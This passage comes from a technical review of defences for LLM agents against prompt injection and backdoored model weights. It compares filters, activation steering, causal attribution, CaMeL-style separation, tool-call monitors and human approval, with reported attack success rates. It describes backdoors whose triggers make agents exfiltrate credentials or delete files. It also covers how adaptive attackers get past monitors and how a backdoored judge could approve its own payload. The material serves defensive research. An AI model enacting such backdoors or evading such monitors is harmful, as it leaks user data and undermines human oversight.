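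A tester who looked only for the original payload after the first step would have passed 75 of the 100 models, including all 19 that still recognised the trigger. Some of those 19 would have transferred money instead of deleting a file, because the second backdoors drew on the same set of harmful payloads as the first. A real defender should choose a harmless payload, and a tester should look for any unexpected tool call.

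A model that recognises a trigger and does nothing harmful isn't an immediate danger, but later training might give the trigger a payload again. The experiments stop after the second step, so they don't show how easily this could happen. An operator usually can't measure recognition, since a real attacker has no reason to make the model announce it, and a model may still notice the trigger without outputting a phrase that says so.

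Huang and colleagues also examined one treated model with a tool that estimates which words each layer makes more likely. The model completed the user's task correctly, but words related to the trigger still ranked among the top ten at some layers. This is only weak evidence that the treated model still detects the trigger, because such words were also prominent when the backdoored model processed a harmless internet address before treatment.

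After retraining, an operator can report how often the tested triggers produced the payload, but can't conclude that the model has no backdoor, because an untested trigger might still work.

### Pruning

Pruning removes parts of a model instead of training them to behave differently. A defender runs the model on clean inputs, finds neurons that are rarely active and switches them off, because a backdoor may depend on them. The defender doesn't need to know the trigger. Pruning can also disable neurons that clean fine-tuning may hardly change because its examples never activate them.

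Lazarus would be the best target for pruning because it uses a few nearly dormant neurons. SilentCall may have no such small group to remove. Backdoors can also use parts that the model needs. Bouger and colleagues cite work on a trigger that switched the output language. The attention heads it used (the components that relate tokens to one another) largely overlapped with those that normally control language. Pruning inactive parts would miss these heads, and removing them could harm the model's ordinary work. In another study they cite, researchers suppressed a backdoor by switching off about 3% of attention heads, but they had first traced which heads it used.

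In *Fine-Pruning* (2018), Liu, Dolan-Gavitt and Garg compared pruning with fine-tuning. According to Huang and colleagues, the paper found that either method alone could fail against a sophisticated backdoor, while using both weakened or removed some attacks. Pruning is therefore a reasonable addition to retraining, but the operator would still have to test the result.

### Replacing, retraining or restricting the model

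Replacing the checkpoint is usually the best choice when a trustworthy alternative exists. An operator with enough clean data to retrain a suspect model can often use the same data to fine-tune a trusted one, at a similar cost and without inheriting the backdoor. The replacement shouldn't be built on the same base model if that model is suspect. Replacing the model helps only if the redirected tool calls came from the weights rather than from, for example, a skill file.

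Retraining makes more sense when the trigger is known and the model has abilities the operator can't reproduce elsewhere. The operator should train the model on correct responses to triggered requests, then test it with other dates, languages, locations and tools and, as Help Net Security recommends, with different input lengths. If the trigger is unknown, the two-step method of Huang and colleagues is worth trying in an isolated environment, but its results don't yet justify restoring the model's full permissions.

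Restricting the agent's tools helps even if every attempt to remove the backdoor has failed. Matsuoka notes that an agent without write access can't delete protected data on its own, and that a model cut off from the network can't send anything out. These restrictions also limit what the agent can do for the user. In the running example, it could still summarise a report that the user had downloaded and draft the email to Ana, but the user would have to send it.

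## Stopping external content from steering tool calls

Most defences against prompt injection assume that the model is sound and the danger comes from the text it reads. Some try to keep planted instructions away from the model or make it less likely to follow them. Others assume the model will sometimes follow planted instructions, and limit what those instructions can change. An operator running a downloaded checkpoint also needs to know how well each defence works if the model has a backdoor.

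### Filters and markers

A filter checks each tool result before the agent's model reads it and deletes or blocks text that looks like an attack. It is usually a small classifier trained on attacks and harmless text. In the running example, it would have to delete the planted paragraph and keep the figures for Ana's summary.

Marking keeps all the text but labels it. Spotlighting delimits or encodes external content to show the model where it came from. Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the content. Both rely on the model following the label, but Ye and colleagues found that such markers hardly changed how a model represented a passage.

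Russinovich compared these defences on gpt-oss-20b, an open model, using 180 attack cases from AgentDojo. He ran each defence beside its own undefended agent.

| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks completed, compared with no defence |
|---|---|---|
| None | 48.3% | 100% |
| Spotlighting | 42.0% | 92.5% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 31.6% | 88.2% |
| PromptGuard-2 filter | 20.5% | 100% |
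| DeBERTa filter | 3.4% | 47.2% |
| PIGuard filter | 1.1% | 58.2% |

The two filters that stopped nearly all attacks also deleted so much harmless text that the agent lost about half its usefulness. PromptGuard-2 shows little or no loss of usefulness in the last column, which covers only runs without an attack. During an attack, it deleted the whole poisoned message, including the information the user wanted, and the agent completed about 31% of its tasks, compared with 55% with no filter.

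Tool descriptions need screening too. In tests on small open models, Dolcetti and colleagues found that a detector flagged every poisoned set of tools but also a very high share of clean ones. It worked better to have a second language model write new descriptions from the tools' code alone, which reduced the success rate of poisoned descriptions to zero. This method requires access to the code, which an operator who connects to somebody else's server usually doesn't have.

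### Training models to rank instructions

Developers can also train a model to prioritise instructions by source, with the system prompt above the user and the user above a web page. StruQ and SecAlign, the two defences that Chen and colleagues tested against their backdoor, do a simple version of this. Both train the model on examples that contain planted instructions, so that it learns to ignore them and answer the user's request.

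SecAlign did well in Russinovich's tests, particularly against argument manipulation. He tried 24 wordings on each of 18 cases. Without a defence, at least one wording succeeded in each of the 18 cases, but with SecAlign this happened in only one case. However, SecAlign's training data included the same families of wording, so the result is weak evidence of how well it resists wordings it was not trained on.

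### Attackers who adapt

Researchers tested most published defences against a fixed list of attacks. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 defences against attackers who kept revising their text in response to the results. The attackers were automated search programs, models trained by reinforcement learning, and more than 500 people in an online competition. They succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although the original tests had mostly found success rates near zero.

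Spotlighting and prompt sandwiching let through as few as 1% of the fixed attacks but more than 95% of the adapted ones. For MetaSecAlign, a later version of SecAlign, the attack success rate rose from 2% with fixed attacks to 96% with adapted ones. PIGuard was the most resistant of four filters, but it still let through 71% of the adapted attacks. A few of the 12 defences target users who try to misuse a model, not prompt injection, but adapted attacks were more successful than fixed ones against both kinds of defence.

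These attackers had large computing budgets, and their search program could see the filters' confidence scores. Someone who plants text on a web page for an unknown agent to read has neither advantage. The 90% success rate therefore can't be assumed for real attacks, and Nasr and colleagues still recommend filters for blocking unsophisticated ones. But the results show that a near-zero success rate on a fixed list of attacks is no evidence of safety against a determined attacker.

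### CounterSteer

Filters have to classify text as malicious or harmless, and an attacker can search for text that they misclassify. Russinovich's CounterSteer changes how the model processes every token of every tool result, without classifying any of it.

The method relies on the model's internal activations, the numbers it computes for each token at each layer. Russinovich prepares it separately for each model:

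1. Collect pairs of runs that differ in whether the model followed a planted instruction.
2. Average the activations over the planted text for each group, and subtract one average from the other. The difference is a direction associated with treating text as an instruction.
3. Check that the direction has an effect. Subtracting it should make the model follow fewer planted instructions, and adding it should make the model follow more.
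4. In use, subtract it from the activations of every tool-result token while the model is reading.

If $h$ is the activation at one token, $\hat d$ the direction, $\sigma$ the typical spread of activations along it and $\alpha$ the chosen strength, the new activation is

$$h' = \|h\| \cdot \frac{h - \alpha\sigma\hat d}{\|h - \alpha\sigma\hat d\|}.$$

The fraction has length one, and multiplying by $\|h\|$ restores the original length, so the edit changes the activation's direction but not its size.

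| Model | Attacks that succeeded, no defence | With CounterSteer | Ordinary tasks completed, compared with no defence |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-20b | 47.5% | 7.9% | 94.4% |
| Qwen3-30B | 48.9% | 7.2% | 94.1% |
| Gemma-4-31B | 23.9% | 0.6% | 92.9% |
| GLM-4.5-Air | 22.2% | 5.6% | 100% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 10.0% | 5.0% | 100% |

These runs are separate from the comparison with filters, in which CounterSteer let through 9.1% of attacks on gpt-oss-20b and kept 90.6% of ordinary performance. On that model, all the attacks that got past CounterSteer were in tasks where the user had told the agent to act on the content. CounterSteer isn't designed to stop those attacks.

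It also worked fairly well against AutoDojo, an automated attacker that rewrote each injection up to six times against the live agent. AutoDojo's success rate fell from 67% to 18% on gpt-oss-20b and from 73% to 19% on Qwen3-30B. PromptGuard-2 performed little better than no defence. An attacker who knew the exact direction and strength succeeded in only 2 of 52 cases.

CounterSteer is still weakest against argument manipulation. In the search over 24 wordings, at least one got past it in 13 of 18 argument manipulation cases, compared with 3 of 18 for tool hijacking. Russinovich had been able to detect the decision while the model was writing the argument, but editing the activations at that point didn't help.

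CounterSteer needs access to the model's internals, so operators who use a model through a provider's service can't install it. It can also make the model worse at reasoning about what it retrieves. When Russinovich put test questions inside tool results, arithmetic scores didn't change, but multiple-choice accuracy fell by about 11 percentage points and instruction-following by about 15. Russinovich designed both the defence and most of the attacks on it, and six rounds of rewriting is a modest effort compared with that of Nasr and colleagues.

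### Testing what a call depends on

Causal attribution tries to identify what caused a pending tool call. If the agent is about to email a stranger, the defence checks whether it would still send the email without the suspicious part of the page it read.

*AgentSentry* saves the agent's state each time a tool returns something. It then replaces the user's request with a question asking the model whether the content is trying to control the agent and, if so, which words do it. Deleting those words gives a cleaned copy of the page. The defence runs the original request on both versions without executing any calls, and computes

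$$S = \hat p_{\text{original}}(a) - \hat p_{\text{cleaned}}(a),$$

where $a$ is the pending call and $\hat p$ is the share of runs in which it appears. The published tests used one run per version, so a call that disappears after cleaning scores 1 and a call that remains scores 0.

A score of 1 raises an alarm only if the question about control also prompted the model to propose an action and that action disappears after cleaning. Two further rules check for influence that builds up or takes effect over several steps. After an alarm, the agent continues from the cleaned page, so Ana can still get her summary.

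The next table compares AgentSentry with other methods that re-run the agent or remove text to find the source of a tool call. Each range covers the results for GPT-4o, GPT-3.5-turbo and Qwen3-Max on AgentDojo, averaged over three attack types.

| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | User's tasks completed under attack | Harmless tasks interrupted |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 26–39% | 40–58% | 0% |
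| CausalArmor | 12–13% | 48–56% | 45–66% |
| AttriGuard | 2–7% | 68–75% | 21–26% |
| MELON | 1–2% | 28–41% | 14–24% |
| AgentSentry | 0% | 72–82% | 2–5% |

AgentSentry stopped all 949 attacks on each model, which is compatible with a true attack success rate of up to 0.39%. Its advantage in completed tasks comes from letting the agent continue after an alarm. A version that stopped the agent instead blocked as many attacks but completed 55% of the tasks in one set, compared with 92% for AgentSentry.

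In harder tests, where planted text had to travel through memory, several documents or up to 24 steps, 11 of 96 attacks succeeded. Of 19 attacks that were written to defeat AgentSentry and worked on the undefended agent, two succeeded. Both gave a false recipient as a plain fact, the same kind of text that defeats CounterSteer. On harmless tasks, the repeated runs raised the average time from 17 to 38 seconds and used 2.5 times as many tokens.

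MELON's record is a reason for caution about the whole approach. MELON runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a request to summarise the tool results, and raises an alarm if the same tool calls appear in both runs. Nasr and colleagues got past it 76% of the time without using knowledge of how it worked, and 95% when they used that knowledge. Nobody has yet independently tested AgentSentry in the same way.

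### CaMeL

In separation by design, the model that decides which tools to call never reads external content, so the defence doesn't depend on recognising an attack or on how the model represents text. In 2023, Simon Willison proposed an early version with two language models. A planner sees the user's request and controls the tools, while a reader sees the external content and has no tools. In 2025, researchers at Google DeepMind and elsewhere published CaMeL, which adds a check on where each value came from. Willison (2025) describes how CaMeL works in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*.

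In the running example, the planner sees the user's request, the contact list and the tool descriptions. It writes a short program, roughly like this:

```python
page = fetch_url("https://reports.example.com")
summary = ask_reader("Summarise this report", page)
send_email(to="ana@example.com", body=summary)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary software and not a language model, then runs the program:

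1. It fetches the page and stores it in a variable. The planner doesn't see the text.
2. It gives the page to the reader, which returns a summary.
3. It attaches tags to each value. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), these record the value's sources and who may read it. The summary inherits the page's tags because it came from the page.
4. Before sending the email, it checks the recipient, the body and their tags against a policy that the operator or user has written.

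| Value | Source | Can the page change it? |
|---|---|---|
| Web address | User's request | No |
| Page | reports.example.com | Yes |
| Summary | Reader, from the page | Yes |
| Ana's address | Contact list | No |

If the page contains the planted paragraph with a stranger's address, the reader may obey it and write a strange summary, but it can't call `send_email`, and the program already names Ana as the recipient. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls this property control-flow integrity. The agent's calls stay within a program determined by the user's request and other trusted information. External content can affect which of the program's existing branches runs, but it can't add a new one.

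The tags matter when a tool call needs an argument from the page. If the user asks the agent to send the summary to the contact listed in the report, the planner has to write a program that gets the address from the reader. With the two models alone, a planted address would go straight into `send_email`. CaMeL tags the address as coming from a web page, so the policy can block the email or require the user's approval. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reproduces this in a formal model of CaMeL, where an address taken from an email stays marked as untrusted all the way to the recipient field.

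### What separation costs and misses

With OpenAI's o3 model, CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and used about 2.8 times as many tokens. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites these figures from the CaMeL paper. The loss of seven percentage points is modest, but it will be larger for agents that can't plan before reading. A coding agent, for example, often has to see an error message before it can decide what to do next.

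Someone also has to write the policies, and users have to approve exceptions. Willison worries that users who see many approval requests will start accepting all of them. CaMeL doesn't try to prevent false statements in the summary, so planted text can still mislead Ana.

Information can also leak through the program's choices. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives an example in which the program asks the reader a question about private notes, then sends 1 or 0 depending on the answer. Neither number came from the notes, so neither has a private tag, but the recipient learns the answer. Errors can leak information in a similar way because they can change which part of a Python program runs next. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) recommends replacing Python with a more restricted language, partly for this reason.

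### Later systems

When several agents work together, protecting each one with CaMeL doesn't protect the whole system. Peters-Gill and colleagues planted an instruction in a database of job applicants. The first agent read the database and the second summarised the result, and both kept the text away from their planners. But the second agent put the summary into its request to a third agent, whose planner treated the whole request as trusted and emailed the applicants' details to the attacker.

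Their solution, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data between agents separately, so the third planner never sees the summary. On their benchmark, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. The gap between agents therefore matters mainly when an attacker targets it. Multi-CaMeL completed fewer tasks, although the loss was modest for the strongest models. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran these tests without policies on the values passed to tools, so the results measure only whether attackers could change which tools the agents called.

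Simpler forms of separation have also worked well. *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw* (2026) tested 649 attacks that had all succeeded against a single agent running GPT-5-mini. Dividing the tools between separate agents reduced the success rate to 0.31%, or two attacks. Making the agents communicate in a fixed data format, without dividing the tools, reduced it to 14.18%. The two measures together stopped every attack. But these attacks were chosen because they had worked on the undefended agent, and an attacker who knew about the separation would write different ones.

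*Twin Agent* (2026) relaxes the requirement to plan first. One agent explores the untrusted material and sends short hints to another, which has permission to act. Limiting the length of the hints makes attacks harder but leaves the acting agent with less information. The design suits coding better than CaMeL does, but it gives up the formal guarantee because a hint can carry an instruction.

Narisetty and colleagues point out that defences outside the model have mostly been tested against fixed attacks, as was true of filters until Nasr and colleagues tested them. They ran a small adaptive test on Progent, which checks tool calls against rules that a language model writes. Progent reduced the average attack success rate from 25.8% to 4.2%, and their adapted attack succeeded only 2.6% of the time. The agent also completed fewer tasks under attack, 27% instead of 45%. They tested one small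 model with one style of attack, and suspect that disguising the instruction from Progent also made it less persuasive to the agent. The result is encouraging but doesn't settle whether a stronger attack would succeed. Narisetty and colleagues work for a security company, and their paper has not been peer-reviewed.

### The same defences with a backdoored model

In the threat model that Narisetty and colleagues describe as standard for this research, the attacker does not control the model's weights. AgentSentry likewise excludes collusion by the model's provider. The papers behind these defences didn't test backdoored models, so most of the table is inferred from how each defence works.

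| Defence | Trigger in the request or the date | Trigger in external content |
|---|---|---|
| Filters and marking | No protection | Little protection, unless a filter happens to delete the trigger |
| CounterSteer | Probably no protection | Unknown; the edit might disrupt the trigger |
| AgentSentry | Probably no alarm | Probably no alarm |
| MELON | Possible alarm for a date, but not for a trigger in the request | Possible alarm |
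| CaMeL with a backdoored planner | The planner can write the malicious call | The planner doesn't see the trigger |
| CaMeL with a backdoored reader | The reader can falsify values if it sees the trigger | The reader can falsify values |

Filters and training against planted instructions offer little protection against a backdoor trigger that contains no instruction. Chen and colleagues showed that a backdoor can also defeat two of these training defenses, StruQ and SecAlign, when the payload arrives as an instruction.

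CounterSteer edits only tool results. Russinovich found that a model given no tool results produces exactly the same output with or without the defence, so SilentCall's date trigger would work unchanged on the agent's first call. If the trigger is in a tool result, the edit might disrupt it by accident, but nobody has measured this.

AgentSentry would miss a date trigger because the page contains no controlling text. The cleaned page would be identical to the original, so both runs would contain the malicious call and the score would be zero. AgentSentry would probably also miss a trigger in the page, because the model would not report a harmless-looking string as an attempt at control. The replay test described earlier avoids this problem by replacing all the external content, not only the instructions.

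MELON might accidentally do better. It runs the agent a second time without the user's request but with the same tool results and, presumably, the same date. If a backdoored model makes the same malicious upload in both runs, MELON would raise an alarm but wrongly attribute the upload to the tool results.

CaMeL relies heavily on the planner being trustworthy. A planner with a date-triggered backdoor could write `stranger@example.net` directly into the program. A policy that checks only for untrusted sources would probably accept the address, because it didn't come from the page. The agent would still satisfy the definition of control-flow integrity, because the request and the date, both trusted, determined the program. The planner could also copy the contact list from its prompt into the email as plain text, and the interpreter might not attach a privacy tag to it. Private files that a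 tool fetches later would keep their tags, so a policy on who may read them could still prevent them from being leaked.

Separation protects the planner from triggers in external content. The string that activated the coding backdoor of Syros and colleagues would stay in a variable that the planner never reads. A trigger based on input length is also less likely to activate, because the planner's input doesn't include downloaded pages. But this protection can fail between agents. A summary that carries an instruction into the next planner could also carry a trigger, and a short trigger could fit inside one of Twin Agent's hints.

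A backdoored reader is less dangerous because it has no tools. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* assumes an honest reader in the ideal agent it uses for comparison. A backdoored reader could misreport the figures or return the attacker's address as Ana's, but the interpreter assigns the tags, so it would still mark the false address as coming from the web page. CaMeL already has to handle a reader hijacked by planted text, and its policies apply equally to one with altered weights, though they can't correct a false summary in either case.

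An operator who uses CaMeL should therefore choose the planner more carefully than the reader. Willison notes that the reader can be a smaller model running on the user's own machine. A downloaded checkpoint is safer as the reader than as the planner, and using it for both would let a backdoor control the plan as well. Policies that check the destination itself, not only its source, also help. A rule that allows emails only to people on the contact list would stop a message to the stranger even if the planner had written the address.

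## Checking each call before it runs and limiting the damage

A tool call does no harm until it runs. In $\text{call} = f(W, R, E)$, a backdoor replaces the weights $W$ and an injection replaces the external content $E$, but a check between the model and the tool only has to inspect the resulting call. The harness can block an email to a stranger even if nobody has found the trigger or the planted paragraph, or worked out which attack produced the address. Pallakonda and colleagues argue that a backdoored model can pass every benchmark but has to emit the payload to do damage. The argument applies equally to injections.

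The check only works if it runs before the tool does. For tools that run on a provider's servers, the operator usually sees the call too late to block it, and has to rely on the provider's controls or switch the tool off. Checking calls also does little about harm caused by what the model writes. For example, the harness will still send a summary containing a false figure if the recipient is correct.

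### SilentCall's two-stage monitor

Pallakonda and colleagues built a monitor that separates two questions. Whether a call is dangerous in itself depends only on the call, so a small, fast model can judge it. Whether the user's request justifies the call depends on the conversation, which takes a larger and slower model to read. The version they recommend works like this:

1. A classifier reads the name and arguments of every call and rates the call safe, warning or critical.
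2. Calls rated safe or warning run immediately.
3. Critical calls go to a judge, a general-purpose language model that reads the conversation up to that point. It decides whether the call directly serves the request or is a proportionate step towards it.
4. If the judge decides against the call, or gives an answer that the software can't parse, the monitor blocks it.

The classifier has 66 million parameters, about one sixtieth as many as the smaller backdoored model. Pallakonda and colleagues trained it on 11,671 calls that a large language model had written and labelled. It checks each call in about 4 milliseconds on a GPU and 29 on a CPU.

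They tested the monitor on 10,007 shell commands from the conversations they had used to train the backdoored models. Of these, 6,826 were legitimate and 3,181 performed the malicious upload. The first row of the table shows the results for the classifier alone, and the other rows show the results with a judge added.

| Calls sent to the judge | Judge | Payloads caught | Legitimate calls wrongly flagged | Share of calls sent to the judge | Average time added per call |
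|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | None | 100% | 16.35% | 0% | 4 ms |
| Critical | Qwen3.5-2B | 100% | 1.73% | 42.9% | 520 ms |
| Warning and critical | Qwen3.5-2B | 100% | 4.45% | 63.2% | 764 ms |
| Critical | gpt-5-nano | 100% | 0.67% | 42.9% | 1,990 ms |
| Critical | Qwen3.5-0.8B | 99.94% | 0.73% | 42.9% | 658 ms |

The judge helps mainly by reducing false alarms. The classifier wrongly flagged some harmless diagnostic commands, such as one that lists the files a program has open. It also wrongly flagged some commands that really are risky, such as scheduling a recurring job or deleting files in bulk, but whether those are appropriate can be determined only from the user's request.

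Pallakonda and colleagues recommend the setup in the second row, which uses an open model that an operator can run locally. It is nearly four times faster than gpt-5-nano, a commercial model, but its false alarm rate is about one percentage point higher.

The figures of 42.9% and 520 milliseconds come from a test in which almost a third of the calls were malicious. The classifier rated all of those critical, along with 16.35% of the legitimate calls, so an agent that is not under attack would send only about 16% of its calls to the judge. Each of those would wait about 1.2 seconds, but the average delay across all calls would be nearer 200 milliseconds.

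A judge can also make detection worse. The smallest judge, Qwen3.5-0.8B, released two payloads that the classifier had correctly flagged. In both conversations the user had asked about credentials for Amazon's storage service, which the malicious upload also used, so the upload looked relevant. In an earlier test with the judge's temperature at 1.0, a common default, detection fell to 73% and the false-positive rate rose to 29%. Operators who adopt the design should therefore keep its greedy decoding.

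### What the false alarms mean in daily use

If an agent makes 1,000 legitimate calls a day, the monitor wrongly blocks about 17 of them at its false-positive rate of 1.73%. The classifier alone would wrongly block about 164.

How many alarms are real depends on how common attacks are. If one call in 10,000 is malicious and the monitor catches every malicious call, the chance that a given alarm is real is

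$$\frac{0.0001 \times 1}{0.0001 \times 1 + 0.9999 \times 0.0173} \approx 0.0057,$$

or about one in 174. An operator would spend ten days dismissing some 173 false alarms for each real one. The 0.67% rate of gpt-5-nano would improve this to about one in 68, and the classifier alone would give about one in 1,636.

The rate of one malicious call in 10,000 is invented, and it fits occasional injections better than an active backdoor. Once SilentCall's trigger date arrives, the model adds the upload to almost every request, so alarms would jump from 17 a day to hundreds, all for the same destination. Software that groups alarms by destination would make this obvious. A backdoor with a rare trigger would not cause this jump.

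The false-positive rate comes from synthetic conversations about software engineering. They contained thousands of different commands, so the test was fairly broad, but an agent that administers servers would legitimately run many more of the commands that the classifier rates critical.

### Why one payload doesn't establish coverage

All 3,181 malicious calls were the same command. The classifier reads only the call, not the conversation, so it received the same input and gave the same score every time. Its 100% detection rate is effectively one success. The judge's test was harder because the conversations differed, and the result for Qwen3.5-2B shows that it consistently recognised this payload in different settings. Pallakonda and colleagues say that coverage of other payloads is a separate question, and they give no confidence interval for detection.

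The payload was also fairly easy to recognise. It sent the machine's environment variables to outside storage, and the classifier's labelling rules listed credential theft among the attacks to rate critical. The exact command wasn't in the classifier's training data, but the storage address contained "exfil" (short for exfiltration), which a careful attacker would leave out. Because there was only one payload, there is no way to tell how much the address helped the classifier.

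Even this payload was hard to separate from legitimate work by score alone, and one legitimate command scored higher than it did. When the threshold for a critical rating was raised to 0.99, the classifier's false positives fell to 5.0% and it still caught the payload, but at 0.999 it missed every copy.

Other payloads might never reach the judge. Destructive file operations count as warnings under the labelling rules, because developers often have good reasons to delete files. The recommended monitor lets warnings run, so it might well allow the Kerkoporta payload that deletes the user's working files. Also sending warnings to the judge would fix this, but with the higher false-positive rate shown in the table.

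A call can also be wrong without looking dangerous. If the classifier receives a `send_email` call with an address and a summary of a report, nothing in the call shows that the address should have been Ana's, so the classifier would probably rate it safe. Its training data included some emails, but the test contained only shell commands, so its performance on emails hasn't been measured.

### Guardrails that look in the wrong place

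Back-Reveal, the backdoor that hides a user's details inside a search request, shows how much it matters where a check is placed. Zhang and Pei tested it against NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, two widely available packages that filter the input and output of language models. They used the default settings for retrieved text, so both packages examined the passages returned by the attacker's server.

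When the server returned only relevant information, 99.2% of passages got past NeMo Guardrails and 98.8% got past LLM Guard. The passages were harmless, and the theft happened in the outgoing request.

Zhang and Pei didn't test how well the same packages would work if an operator configured them to inspect outgoing calls. But their result does show that an operator can install a well-known guardrail, see it running, and have no protection against this attack.

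Zhang and Pei suggest several controls on the call itself, and leave testing them to future work:

- Allow web requests only to approved hosts, and limit how much data a request may carry.
- Flag arguments that contain long, unreadable strings or text derived from the user's stored details.
- Stop an agent that has read private memory from sending anything out without separate permission.

The list of approved hosts looks the most dependable because it works however the attacker disguises the data. A check for unreadable strings fails if the model can write the same details as ordinary search words. The last control would stop the attack directly, but it would also interrupt a lot of legitimate work. For example, an assistant that looks up a user's city and then checks the local weather takes the same two steps, in the same order, as the attack.

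### Controls on the running example

The table shows what each control would do about the three altered calls in the running example, based on how the controls work rather than on an experiment.

| Control | Fetch through the relay | Extra email to a stranger | Contact list sent to a stranger |
|---|---|---|---|
| Schema validation | Lets it through | Lets it through | Lets it through |
| Comparing arguments with the request | Stops it | Stops it | Stops it |
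| Allowed sites and recipients | Stops it | Stops it | Stops it |
| Permission to draft emails but not send them | No effect | Stops it | Stops it |
| Restricted outbound traffic | Stops it | Lets it through if the mail server is allowed | Lets it through if the mail server is allowed |
| Human approval with the raw arguments | Stops it if the person notices | Stops it if the person notices | Stops it if the person notices |

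#### Schema validation

Schema validation checks only the format of a call, so an attacker's address passes as easily as a genuine one. It is still worth having because it catches malformed calls. It becomes a security control only if the schema lists the permitted values, such as the addresses in the contact list.

#### Comparing arguments with the request

The user named one site and one person, so the harness can work out before the agent starts that the task needs a fetch from reports.example.com and an email to Ana's address. It then compares each call with those values. The comparison has to examine the right part of the address, because the relay's address contains the genuine one:

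```python
url = "https://relay.example.net/?target=https://reports.example.com"

"reports.example.com" in url                     # True
urlsplit(url).hostname == "reports.example.com"  # False
```

The first test would approve the relay. The second extracts the name of the site that the harness would actually contact, and rejects it.

This control is the most precise of the six, but it works only when the user's request specifies the arguments. If the user asks for "recent news about the company", there is no site to check the call against. If the user gives only a name, such as "Ana", the harness should look up the address in the contact list rather than ask the agent's own model, which may be the component at fault.

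#### Allowed sites and recipients

A fixed list of allowed values doesn't depend on how the user words the request. It suits agents with a narrow job, such as one that reads reports from a few sites and emails colleagues. But it accepts any value on the list, so an attacker could still redirect a salary file to the wrong colleague if that colleague's address is allowed.

Entries also need to be specific. SilentCall uploads to an account on Amazon's storage service. A developer who keeps files on that service might allow all of it, including the attacker's account. PromptArmor's demonstration against Claude Cowork exploited the same kind of gap by sending data out through an interface that the restrictions permitted.

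#### Narrow permissions

Permissions limit what any call can do, including calls that pass every check. An agent that can only draft emails can't send the contact list anywhere. If the harness looks up Ana's address, the model doesn't need the contact list in its context and so can't leak it. Narrow permissions don't stop the fetch from going through the relay, but the relay can't collect login details if the fetch tool holds none.

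Removing one tool achieves little if another can do the same job. An agent with a general command line can usually fetch pages and send data without the tools the operator restricted. Lazarus's short download-and-run command, for instance, needs only a command line and a network connection.

#### Restricted outbound traffic

Network rules apply to everything the agent's machine sends, whichever tool or program sends it. They help when checking a call isn't enough, because a command that runs a script doesn't show what the script will do. If the script tries to contact a host that isn't on the allowed list, the rules block the connection. A sandbox, an isolated environment with its own files and few privileges, also limits what the script can read or damage.

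Neither measure helps much with the two emails. They leave through the company's mail server, which the agent must reach to do its job, so the operator needs a rule about recipients in the harness or on the mail server.

### Warning labels on tools

Some operators try to get a similar effect by adding warnings to the text the model reads. Han (2026) tested such warnings in *Weighing the Envelope*. An attacker had already installed a malicious tool, and the agent had false memories of the user approving it. The user then made an ordinary request that could lead the agent to call the tool.

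Without a warning, the agents failed to refuse in 90.6% of runs. A label telling the model to inspect the tool's code first, and not to use the tool if it couldn't, reduced this to 9.4%. Adding a false memory of approval raised the rate to 61.7%, and a note before the memories saying they were unverified lowered it to 4.4%. The label could prevail over the false memory with GLM, but not with DeepSeek or MiniMax.

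Han concludes that labels are a soft gate and can't replace permissions, sandboxing or human review. That seems right, since a single false sentence undid most of the protection. The result also suggests that the harness should keep its own record of what the user has approved, because planted text can forge approvals stored in the agent's memory.

Han recommends reporting separately how often the model refused, how often another layer intercepted the attack and how often the attack achieved its goal. A single attack success rate combines these outcomes, so an operator can't tell whether the model refused or the sandbox blocked the attack. This matters for a backdoored model, which may ignore every label while the sandbox still works.

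### When the judge is part of the problem

A language model used as a judge has the same two weaknesses as the agent it checks.

If the agent and the judge run on the same weights, a backdoor affects both. The judge reads the conversation, so a trigger such as the date or a phrase in the request may also be in its context. An attacker who expects the model to check its own calls could train it to approve the payload. None of the studies described here tested a backdoored judge, but a different model costs little to run, so there is no reason to use the same one for both jobs. Ideally the judge should come from a different developer. The judge that Pallakonda and colleagues recommend belongs to the same Qwen family as the models they backdoored, and a backdoor from poisoned pretraining data could be present in both. Their test couldn't show whether this matters, because Gemini or Claude models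 wrote the conversations and software inserted the payload, so none of the calls came from the backdoored models.

Planted text can also reach the judge. The conversation it reads includes the web pages and emails the agent has read, and a page could claim that the user wants a copy sent to the stranger. Pallakonda and colleagues didn't test their judge against such text. Showing the judge only the user's request and the proposed call would remove most of the risk, although the call can still contain planted text, such as a paragraph in the body of an email. A judge that can't see the tool results will also block more legitimate steps, such as a second fetch that only makes sense after reading the first page.

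Rules written in ordinary code don't have either weakness. It makes sense to let code handle whatever it can, such as checking whether an address is on the contact list, and leave the cases that need interpretation to the judge. CaMeL's policies, described in the previous section, are rules of this kind that can also take into account where each value came from.

### Human approval

A person reviewing a call can notice things that no rule anticipated, if the screen shows what the harness is about to execute. If it shows the model's own description instead, such as "Email the summary to Ana", a compromised model can omit the extra recipient, as it does in its replies. The screen should show the tool's name and every argument in full. Shortening long values is dangerous because the relay's address ends with the genuine one, and a narrow box might display only that part.

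Reading the judge's explanation doesn't replace checking the call's arguments, because the explanation can be wrong even when the decision is right. Pallakonda and colleagues found a case in which Qwen3.5-2B correctly blocked a call but cited a destination that wasn't in the call as its reason.

The main drawback of approval is that it takes up the reviewer's attention. If the agent makes 1,000 legitimate calls a day and each decision takes 30 seconds, approving every call would take more than eight hours a day. Approving only the calls that the classifier rates critical would take about 80 minutes, and reviewing only those that the judge then blocks would take about nine minutes.

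Pallakonda et al. and Willison warn that people also stop reading the alarms. They didn't measure this, but the arithmetic above makes it plausible, since someone who has correctly dismissed 173 alarms in a row has good reason to dismiss the next.

Approval therefore works best for a few actions that are rare and hard to undo, such as deleting shared data, paying money or emailing somebody for the first time. The harness should refuse calls the agent never needs to make, without asking anyone. Approval is also a poor fit for agents that run overnight, because they must either wait until morning for an answer or have permission to continue without one.

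### Microsoft's recommendations

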